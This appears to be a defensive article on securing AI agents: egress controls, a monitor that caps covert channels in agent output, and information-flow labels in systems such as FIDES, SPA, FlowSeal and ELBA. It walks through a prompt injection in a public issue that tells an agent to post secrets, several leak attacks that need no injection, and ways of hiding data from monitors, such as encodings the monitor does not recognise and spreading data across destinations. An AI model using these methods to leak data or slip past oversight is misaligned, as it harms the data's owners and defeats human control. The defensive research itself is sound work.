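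OpenAI now bars high-risk workloads from reaching the internet, either directly or through other services. If their work requires web pages, they can use only a service that supplies stored copies. OpenAI is also isolating, restricting or replacing the supporting services these workloads can still reach. Each high-risk workload has two independent sets of network controls, one around its sandbox and one in the surrounding cluster of machines. Neither a workload nor a compromised service should be able to change its own limits. OpenAI's stated aim is that one compromised workload or service doesn't by itself open a way to the internet (*The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead*, 2026).

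A listed service may also offer functions that the agent doesn't need. A package server can let clients store files, manage accounts and change settings, but an agent that installs software only needs to download packages. The proxy or the server should refuse all other requests, and the agent's credential should not permit them.

OpenAI had taken some of these steps before the main incident. On July 5 and 6, after an earlier compromise, it removed a shared credential from new workloads, blocked the vulnerable paths on the service and restricted the types of requests that agents could make. Tests resumed on July 7, and agents were on the internet again within two days. The repairs fixed the known faults, but the service could still reach the internet, so one unknown fault was enough to defeat them. Cutting the service's own internet access also protects against faults that nobody has found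 yet.

### Watching the permitted traffic

OpenAI is also adding systems that look for intrusions, stolen data and unusual volumes of traffic on approved connections. A package server, for example, normally sends large files to agents and receives short requests. A series of large uploads to it, or requests to its administrative functions, would stand out even though the server is on the allowlist.

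On June 27, a monitoring tool flagged suspicious scanning inside OpenAI's research network, but on-call staff advised that the test didn't need to stop. IANS's *OpenAI's Postmortem Recasts the Hugging Face Breach as an Incident Response Failure* (2026) recommends deciding in advance which unexpected agent behaviour counts as an incident. OpenAI has since adopted such a rule for severe alerts from its monitoring of agents' reasoning and actions. Responders are expected to pause the activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false.

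Isolation can make monitoring harder. Many companies run security software that monitors the programs on employees' computers, but it can't monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards but concedes that this isn't the same as live monitoring.

Jessica Hebenstreit, a member of the IANS faculty, criticised OpenAI for not telling defenders what to do. That seems partly fair, because OpenAI's plan is specific about the kinds of control the company is adding but includes few settings or thresholds that another company could copy. In SC Media, Ziv Karliner, chief executive of Pillar Security, argued that the boundary must cover every system that can receive, trust or act on an agent's output. That includes network services, but also any trusted program outside the sandbox that opens a file the agent wrote.

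### Limits on size and rate

A request can contain stolen data even if its destination, account and operation are all permitted. The issue-reading agent has permission to comment on `acme/app`, and a comment can contain anything. A proxy can still limit how much the agent sends and how often.

Suppose it allows 20 comments a day of up to 2,000 characters each. Base64 text carries 6 bits per character, so a full comment can hold 12,000 bits, or 1,500 bytes:

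| Stolen data | Comments needed | Time at 20 comments a day |
|---|---|---|
| A 256-bit key | 1 | Immediate |
| A 100 kB customer list | 67 | 4 days |
| A 30 MB file | 20,000 | 1,000 days |

The Files API would have accepted the 30 MB file in a single upload. Limits like these make bulk theft slow and easy to notice, and they barely affect an agent that writes short comments. They don't protect the key, which is only 43 characters long. To protect short secrets, the filter would have to limit hidden data separately from ordinary text.

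### A budget for hidden data

*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) describes a monitor that aims to make hidden channels in an agent's outgoing messages too slow to be useful. The design assumes that an attacker already controls what the agent tries to send, but not the monitor. It can't stop every leak, because an agent can always convey one bit by sending a message or staying silent.

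Every outgoing text passes through stages that can approve, rewrite, delay or cancel it. The first stage normalises the text so that messages that look the same are encoded the same way. It deletes invisible characters, replaces foreign letters that look like Latin ones with the Latin letters, and puts the fields of structured data in a standard order. This removes any bits hidden in those details without changing the message a reader sees.

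Later, more intrusive stages can collapse repeated spaces and punctuation, replace synonyms with one standard word, or have a language model rephrase the whole message. Others randomise or regulate the time between messages.

One stage estimates how much hidden data a message could hold and deducts that amount from the destination's budget in a capacity ledger. Each budget is measured in bits and refills at a fixed rate. When the budget runs out, the monitor delays or cancels further suspicious messages. If the budget holds at most *B* bits and refills at *r* bits an hour, the messages counted against it can carry no more than *B* + *rT* bits of hidden data in *T* hours.

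With a budget of 128 bits that refills at 8 bits an hour, leaking a 256-bit key would take 16 hours, since 128 + 8 × 16 = 256. A strict ledger would also block a comment that quotes the identifier of a code change in the agent's diagnosis, because Git commonly uses 40 hexadecimal digits for these identifiers, which can carry 160 bits. Raising the budget to 160 bits would let the identifier through but cut the time needed to leak the key to 12 hours.

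The separate budgets are another weakness, because an agent can send 128 bits to each of two destinations that an attacker can read and so deliver the whole key at once. To prevent this, a company would need a shared limit across all the destinations that outsiders can read. The ledger also counts only data that the monitor recognises as suspicious, so data in an encoding that the monitor doesn't recognise doesn't use up any of the budget.

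### Results and costs

To test the monitor, Metere wrote programs that hid random bits in messages and others that tried to recover them. For each hiding method, he measured the mutual information between a hidden bit *X* and the recovered bit *Y*:

*I*(*X*;*Y*) = Σ *p*(*x*,*y*) log₂ [*p*(*x*,*y*) / (*p*(*x*) *p*(*y*))]

The sum covers the four combinations of hidden and recovered bits. The result is 1 bit if the receiver recovers every bit and 0 if its output is unrelated to what the sender hid. The reduction in capacity is 1 − *I*(*X*;*Y*).

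Metere ran 20 trials of each text method in two modes. The default mode enforces only the stages that leave the visible message unchanged, plus a check for known credentials and other marked data. The other stages only record what they would have done. In full enforcement mode, every stage can act.

| Hiding place | Reduction, default | Reduction, full enforcement |
|---|---|---|
| Invisible characters | 100% | 100% |
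| Look-alike letters | 100% | 100% |
| Order of data fields | 100% | 100% |
| Number of spaces | 0% | 100% |
| Choice of synonyms | 0% | 100% |
| Base64 text | 0% | 100% |
| Average across the benchmark | 60.2% | 100% |

In default mode, the monitor detected the last three hiding methods in every trial but let the messages through, so an administrator would learn of the leak but not prevent it. Rounding the send times left about a fifth of the timing channel open. The channel closed only when messages were released at a constant pace, which makes urgent messages wait.

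Metere attributes the gap between 60.2% and 100% to the need to avoid false positives when a company first installs the monitor. Full enforcement can damage legitimate messages, including long blocks of code and formatted tables. For example, collapsing repeated spaces would break Python code, which uses indentation to mark its structure. If the company exempts code, an attacker can hide data in it. Rephrasing each message requires another model, and if that model is unavailable, the monitor sends the text without rephrasing it.

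The 100% figure applies only to the methods Metere tried. He works for the company behind the system and wrote both the attacks and the defence, so an independent attacker might find encodings he didn't consider. The results are good evidence that the monitor can remove known hiding places, but weaker evidence that few others remain.

### Why content scanning can't settle the matter

Any filter that searches for secrets, including Pipelock's scanner, can catch accidental leaks but may miss a secret that an attacker has disguised. For example, an attacker can have the agent use a code in which ordinary sentences stand for bits. A choice among *N* plausible messages can carry up to log₂ *N* bits, as can a choice among *N* web pages.

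Images and sound make the problem harder. Metere argues that no classifier can reliably distinguish real audio from data turned into audible tones, because a careful attacker can imitate whatever features the classifier uses. His monitor therefore checks media for a digital signature from an approved producer, such as a speech or chart program, and alters any media without one. The signature check doesn't depend on the content, so it would also accept a chart of employees' salaries made by an approved program.

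Normalising and rephrasing preserve a message's meaning, so they don't remove a secret stated in plain words. "Revenue fell by 4% last quarter" would pass through every stage with the figure intact. The finance team may be entitled to that sentence, but it could be a serious leak in a public comment. Because the text is the same in both cases, a scanner also needs information about where the figure came from and who may receive it.

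## 2026: labels in working systems and what they cost

Confidentiality labels can supply information that a content scanner lacks. On May 20, 2026, Microsoft added FIDES, its researchers' label-tracking system, to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes the component as experimental, and so far it works only in Python.

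### Labels in Microsoft Agent Framework

The research version of FIDES labelled data with the set of people who may read it. The product has three confidentiality levels instead:

- Public data may go anywhere.
- Private data is internal to the business and must not leave through a public channel.
- User identity data, the most sensitive level, includes personal details and credentials.

As in the research version, data is also either trusted or untrusted, and combined data takes the most restrictive labels of its inputs. With only six labels, the system is easy to configure but can't distinguish between private documents with different readers. A salary file and a legal memo are both private, so an internal tool that accepts private data would accept either, regardless of who reads the tool's output.

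A developer can set two limits on each sink, which is a tool that sends data out or takes an action. `max_allowed_confidentiality` sets the highest confidentiality level of data the tool accepts. `accepts_untrusted: False` blocks the tool once the context contains untrusted data. Ordinary code checks both limits before the tool runs.

Microsoft's documentation demonstrates this with an agent very like the issue-reading agent. Under its settings, issue 212 would have these effects:

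| Step | Label of the new data | Label of the context | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read issue 212 | Untrusted, public | Untrusted, public | Allowed |
| Read a file of secrets, as the issue asks | Trusted, private | Untrusted, private | Allowed |
| Post the secrets in a public comment | None | Untrusted, private | Refused, because comments accept only public data |

If the issue had asked the agent to change a file instead, the file-writing tool would have blocked the write because the context was untrusted. In both cases, the attacker can completely fool the model without causing the intended damage.

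But the check uses the label of the whole context, not the text of the comment, so a harmless comment would also fail after the second step. In Microsoft's example, the file-reading tool labels every file private, including the source code that the agent is supposed to quote. An agent that read one line of public code could then no longer comment without approval. A developer could avoid this by labelling each file according to who can read its repository.

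The example turns each refusal into an approval request that names the tool and the label responsible. Developers can instead block the call outright. They can also do a dry run, which logs violations without blocking anything, to find out how much legitimate work the policy would stop.

### What happens when a developer forgets a label

Developers have to label each data source themselves. Microsoft's launch post says the framework treats unlabelled data as trusted and public. But the documentation gives the default for unlabelled tool results as untrusted and public, and describes this as a design that "fails closed rather than open".

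That description is correct only for integrity. Suppose a developer adds a tool that reads customer records and forgets to label its results. In a session that contains nothing else, the default would reverse both decisions:

| Next action | With the correct label (trusted, user identity) | With the default label (untrusted, public) |
|---|---|---|
| Change a file | Allowed | Refused |
| Post the record in a public comment | Refused | Allowed |

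The documentation also describes a fallback in which a result inherits the labels of the tool's arguments. This wouldn't help, because a public customer number can be used to look up a record that isn't public.

A developer can change the default confidentiality to private. Any unlabelled tool would then block public comments until someone labelled it. This would interrupt some legitimate work, but a developer would notice the interruption, whereas a leak under the public default might go unnoticed.

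Microsoft lists several other limits. Once an untrusted issue enters the context, the rest of the run stays untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes it. Approval requests don't explain the full reasoning behind a refusal. The isolated model that reads hidden text can answer only one prompt at a time. Microsoft is considering labels that apply to single messages and labels that relax when the agent condenses its history. The second idea needs care, because a condensed history can still contain the secret.

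### Where labels come from

Access lists are a good source of confidentiality labels because services already maintain them. GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol can attach labels based on who may see each item. Its code documentation on pkg.go.dev shows that checking whether a repository is public is not enough, because draft releases, collaborator lists and security alerts are private even in a public repository. If a search finds nine public repositories and one private one, the whole result is labeled private.

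Integrity is harder to determine. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes files and issues from private repositories as trusted, while the code documentation treats issue text as untrusted in every repository. The stricter rule seems safer because an employee might paste a stranger's email into a private issue.

Access lists also change, so a label can become outdated. Microsoft's prototype for Teams, its workplace chat service, looks up a channel's current members before the agent posts there. If the context is untrusted and some members aren't entitled to the message, the prototype prompts the user to decide whether to post it and lists those members. Users can answer that more easily than a prompt about a long shell command. If the context is trusted, the message goes through without a prompt, as under the FIDES email rule.

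For servers that don't supply labels, Microsoft has published a gateway that adds them. A company using it has to write a labelling function and write or choose a policy for each tool. Software can also infer rough labels from servers' descriptions of their tools. It could mark results as private if the tool requires a login, and as untrusted if the tool reads from the open internet. This saves work, but an inaccurate description would produce an inaccurate label.

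Many companies put sensitivity labels such as "Confidential" on documents. The labels help only if they stay attached when an agent uses the document. Microsoft's *Manage Sensitivity Labels for Agent Embedded File Content* warns that a badly configured agent can become "a label-stripping mechanism", because a file embedded in the agent loses the protection it had in its original location.

People can assign labels too. GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs agents on repositories, ranks content by its author and by whether a maintainer has approved it. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* gives five levels:

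| Level | Typical content |
|---|---|
| Merged | Changes that a maintainer has accepted into the main code |
| Approved | Content from owners, members and collaborators, and everything in private repositories |
| Unapproved | Content from outside contributors |
| None | Content from strangers |
| Blocked | Content from banned users |

By default, GitHub shows agents only approved or merged content in public repositories, and applies no filter in private ones. The public default would hide issue 212 from the agent, along with every genuine bug report from a stranger. A maintainer can approve an issue by adding a designated label or, if the project enables the option, a thumbs-up. The maintainer has to notice any malicious instructions before approving it, and an attacker who takes over a maintainer's account can approve anything.

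A classifier could label documents that have no access list or human label, but some of its labels would be wrong, and the software that enforces labels can't correct them. If the classifier marks a customer list as public, software that enforces the policy perfectly will still let the agent publish the list.

### Confidential emails in Copilot

In January 2026, Microsoft 365 Copilot Chat was summarising emails labelled confidential. *Microsoft Copilot Bug Exposes Confidential Emails, Risking CX Data Security* (Willing, 2026) dates the first detection to January 21. Some affected customers had also set up a data loss prevention policy meant to stop Copilot from processing labelled messages. According to Petri's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Bug Exposes Confidential Emails Despite DLP Safeguards*, Microsoft confirmed in a notice that Copilot was summarising emails despite the label and the policy.

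The fault affected Sent Items and Drafts but not inboxes, and Microsoft blamed a code error, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot*. Sent messages often quote the email they answer, so Copilot could probably read some incoming mail too.

Microsoft began deploying a fix in early February. Office365ITPros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) describes a test done after the fix reached the author's organisation. When asked about a fictitious "Project Bunny", Copilot said it had found an email but could not disclose the contents. The organisation had been affected, but the author learned of the fault only from a reader's comment. CPO Magazine reports that the affected period ended on February 20.

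*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* uses the term "complete mediation" for the principle that every request must pass through the policy check. Copilot violated this principle for two folders. An administrator who tested only the inbox would have found nothing wrong, so a proper test needs a labelled dummy message in every folder and must be repeated after each update.

### Labels that last between requests

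An agent that saves results must also save their labels. Girrens and Wang give the example of a user who asks an agent to save the details of an invoice on Monday and to pay it on Tuesday. If an attacker has changed the account number on the invoice, the payment goes to the attacker, even if the invoice contains no instructions and the agent follows the right steps.

Their system, SPA, stores each result as a value, a label and a short description. For each new request, it works as follows:

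1. The planning model sees the descriptions of stored results, but not the values, and writes a complete plan in a small programming language.
2. Ordinary code traces the labels through the plan and rejects it if any step would violate a policy. This check also covers Denning's implicit flows.
3. If the plan passes, SPA runs it without changes. Each stored value comes back with its original label.

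The model gets no second attempt after a rejection, because repeated revisions could eventually produce an unsafe plan that passes.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA on the AgentDojo benchmark. They also divided each of its 97 tasks into between two and five requests, so that later steps depended on stored results. These are the figures with GPT-5.4 nano, a small model:

| Test | Label checks | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
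|---|---|---|---|
| One request | Off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| One request | On | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Several requests | Off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Several requests | On | 35.3% | 0.2% |

The checks nearly halved the number of completed tasks. Writing the plan before reading any untrusted data had already defeated almost all attacks, so the checks could stop few more. With the checks on, about 53% of single-request runs ended in a label violation, typically because the plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted data.

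The benchmark probably understates the value of the labels, because its attacks were not designed to stay in memory and take effect later. Also, in two of the successes recorded in the multi-request test with checks on, SPA had rejected the plan. With labels, the agent retrieved a stored result it needed in 89.9% of cases, only slightly less often than the 95.4% without them.

Girrens and Wang suggest setting a separate trust requirement for each argument of a tool. A payment tool could require a trusted account number but accept an untrusted description. They also suggest endorsement, which raises the integrity of data after an explicit check. For the invoice, software could endorse the account number if it matched the company's list of suppliers.

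### Leaks without prompt injection

An outsider can also get private data from an agent by making an ordinary but misleading request. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, tested three such attacks on agents that held sensitive information, such as a person's medical diagnosis:

- In the shared-page attack, the outsider creates a document and asks the agent to fill in its section.
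- In the clean-up attack, the outsider lists true and false details about the person and asks the agent to delete the errors. Whatever remains is true.
- In the two-channel attack, an email tells the agent to reply only "completed", while a separate document asks it to write down the details.

Shim and colleagues built FlowSeal, a defence that keeps a register of private records, their owners and the people allowed to receive them. The owner can fill in the register, or software can fill it from access lists and contacts. Code outside the agent tracks which records the agent reads, and it intercepts everything the agent tries to write or share. If the recipient is neither approved nor banned, a separate model compares the outgoing text with the records and returns only "safe" or "blocked".

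The table compares FlowSeal with an earlier defence, a prompt that told the agent to follow a strict procedure for obtaining consent:

| Attack | Sensitive items leaked with the consent prompt | Sensitive items leaked with FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Shared page | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Clean-up | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Two-channel | 43.8% | 2.2% |

The agent also completed more harmless tasks with FlowSeal (72.4%) than with the consent prompt (44.7%). In a small test on real Gmail and Notion accounts, the clean-up attack leaked 34.7% of sensitive items under a different defence and none under FlowSeal.

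However, most of that useful work depended on the separate model. When Shim and colleagues replaced it with a fixed rule that blocked every message to an unknown recipient, the agent completed no harmless tasks. A rule that allowed every such message raised completion to 79.4%, but the shared-page attack leaked 24.9% of sensitive items. The labels determine when a check is necessary, and the separate model decides whether the message may go. FlowSeal's formal guarantee therefore holds only if that model makes no mistakes, and it sometimes misses secrets that the agent has paraphrased.

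FlowSeal also withheld too much. In tests where the owner would have consented, it shared 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for the prompt-based defences. Its checks added about 37% to the running time.

Shim and colleagues argue that FIDES would be vulnerable to their attacks because a language model enforces its policies. They didn't test FIDES, and Microsoft's documentation contradicts their description of it, since ordinary code performs the checks in Agent Framework.

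### Programs with a floating label

FIDES and FlowSeal check tool calls. Zhou and colleagues extended label checks to the programs an agent writes. Their system, ELBA, requires the agent to write in Haskell, where a program's type specifies what effects it can have, such as reading a file or using the network. Before running a program, ELBA checks that it uses only permitted effects. The program can do any calculation but can't open a network connection of its own.

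While the program runs, a floating label covers everything the program has read so far. If the program fetches a page from an untrusted website, the label's integrity drops to the website's level, and any later attempt to write to a trusted destination fails.

The agent can also pass a job to a subagent that has a separate floating label. The subagent might read a web page, write a message based on it, and return that message sealed. The main agent can then send the message through a tool that checks the message's label, without reading the message or changing its own label. Unlike the quarantined model in Willison's Dual LLM design, the subagent can use tools, because its floating label limits what they may do.

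With the policy on, ELBA completed roughly twice as many of AgentDojo's Slack tasks as CaMeL. The policy was still expensive. In Zhou and colleagues' simulation of stronger attacks, it greatly reduced the number of users' tasks that ELBA completed:

| Model | Tasks completed without the policy (of 735) | Tasks completed with the policy (of 735) |
|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 557 | 312 |
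| GPT 5.4 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 494 | 294 |

Under the policy, each model failed 33% to 44% of the tasks it could otherwise complete. All four models are far more capable than those in the original FIDES tests, so better planning alone hasn't stopped strict labels from reducing task completion.

### When labels rise until they mean nothing

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that much of this burden comes from uncertainty about what influences a model's output. If software can't determine which inputs affected an output, every output eventually carries every label, and the labels no longer distinguish one piece of data from another. The paper calls this "label explosion", an extreme form of label creep.

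This can happen quickly with reader lists. Suppose a company has ten employees and each document is open to eight of them, chosen at random. A summary of *n* documents then has an average of 10 × 0.8ⁿ permitted readers, which is about three people after five documents and one after ten. Real access lists overlap more than random ones because teams tend to share the same files, so the number would usually fall more slowly.

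The paper proposes three lines of research:

- **Measure influence.** Labels could state how much information an output carries about each input, so that software could ignore very weak connections.
- **Remove an input and compare.** If the agent would behave the same way without a document, the output may not need that document's label.
- **Examine the model's internal workings.** Researchers could try to trace information from particular inputs to particular outputs.

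None of these methods yet offers the certainty of a conservative label. A small measured influence can still be a serious leak if the secret is short. Comparing outputs requires extra model runs, and a few runs may miss an occasional effect. Tracing information inside a model would require a dependable account of how it works.

Developers can already slow label creep by labelling smaller units, such as individual messages or the text from each website, but only if they also keep those units apart. The documentation for GitHub's server explains that the agent can copy search results anywhere once they are together in its context, so labelling each result separately would give false reassurance.

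The other remedy is to allow exceptions through declassification or endorsement. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests that a digital signature could help justify endorsing technical documentation or a code change. A signature proves who supplied the data but doesn't prove that the data is safe, so a policy still has to specify which signers to trust and for what purpose.

### One label for the whole sandbox

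Labels on tool calls don't extend into ordinary code running in a sandbox. Suppose a coding agent copies a private file and a public one into its sandbox, then runs a script that produces a third file. The label-tracking software detects when the command starts and finishes, but not which files the script used. ELBA can follow the data because the agent writes in a language designed for tracking it, but most coding agents need the shell and existing programs.

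The safe assumption is that anything in the sandbox may have influenced anything that comes out. The sandbox therefore needs one label that combines the labels of everything that has entered it. An egress proxy could use that label to choose which destinations to permit and which credentials to add.

GitHub Agentic Workflows has many of the necessary parts, but GitHub Next says that the system doesn't yet use confidentiality labels to block leaks. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes an agent in a container whose internet traffic passes through a firewall and whose tool calls pass through a separate gateway. In GitHub's architecture guide, a proxy for model traffic can also hold credentials outside the agent's container. The gateway's code documentation on pkg.go.dev describes a record of the confidentiality and integrity tags that each agent has accumulated.

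The following policy is a hypothetical design for the issue-reading agent, not a feature of GitHub's or Microsoft's products:

| Sandbox label | What has entered the sandbox | Permitted traffic | Credential the proxy will add |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted, public | The developer's instructions | Public websites, public packages and `acme/app` | A token that can change `acme/app` |
| Untrusted, public | Issue 212 or public code | Reading `acme/app`, commenting on its issues and downloading public packages | A token that can read `acme/app` and comment |
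| Trusted, private | Code from `acme/billing` | `acme/billing` and an internal package server with no internet access | A token that can read and change `acme/billing` |
| Untrusted, private | Issue 212 and code from `acme/billing` | The internal package server and a private folder for drafts | A token that can add a draft to the folder |
| User identity | A customer's record | The service that holds the record | A token for that customer only |

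The last row needs more detail than Microsoft's three levels provide, because the proxy has to identify which customer the data concerns. In every row, the company that hosts the model must also be entitled to the data, since it receives the agent's context.

The proxy has to change its rules before new data arrives. If it waited until afterwards, a program already running in the sandbox could send the data out in the meantime. The safe order is:

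1. The agent requests some data, and a gateway outside the sandbox finds its label.
2. The gateway combines that label with the sandbox's current label.
3. The proxy switches to the corresponding row of the table and closes any connections the row doesn't permit.
4. The gateway delivers the data.

Under this policy, reading issue 212 moves the sandbox from the first row to the second. If the agent then follows the attacker's instructions and tries to open `acme/billing`, the proxy has no credential to add and refuses the request, so the private code never reaches the sandbox. In Microsoft's example, the agent can read the private file and fails only when it tries to publish the contents.

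The agent can still post its diagnosis on the public issue. The proxy doesn't need to search the comment for secrets, because the sandbox has received only public data. This depends on every label being correct, so the gateway should treat unlabelled data as untrusted and private.

If a developer starts with the private code and then asks the agent to read issue 212, the sandbox moves to the fourth row. The agent can no longer comment in public or change any code. It can save a draft for the developer to check and post, which makes the developer responsible for declassifying it.

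A single label for the sandbox is less precise than a label for each tool call, so it makes label creep worse. The company also can't safely lower the label while the sandbox exists, because private data may remain in a file or a running program. To return to public work, the company has to start a new sandbox.

A task that needs both public comments and private code could use two sandboxes. The agent in the public one could ask the agent in the private one whether `acme/billing` causes the bug and receive only a yes or no. The company would also have to limit the number of questions.
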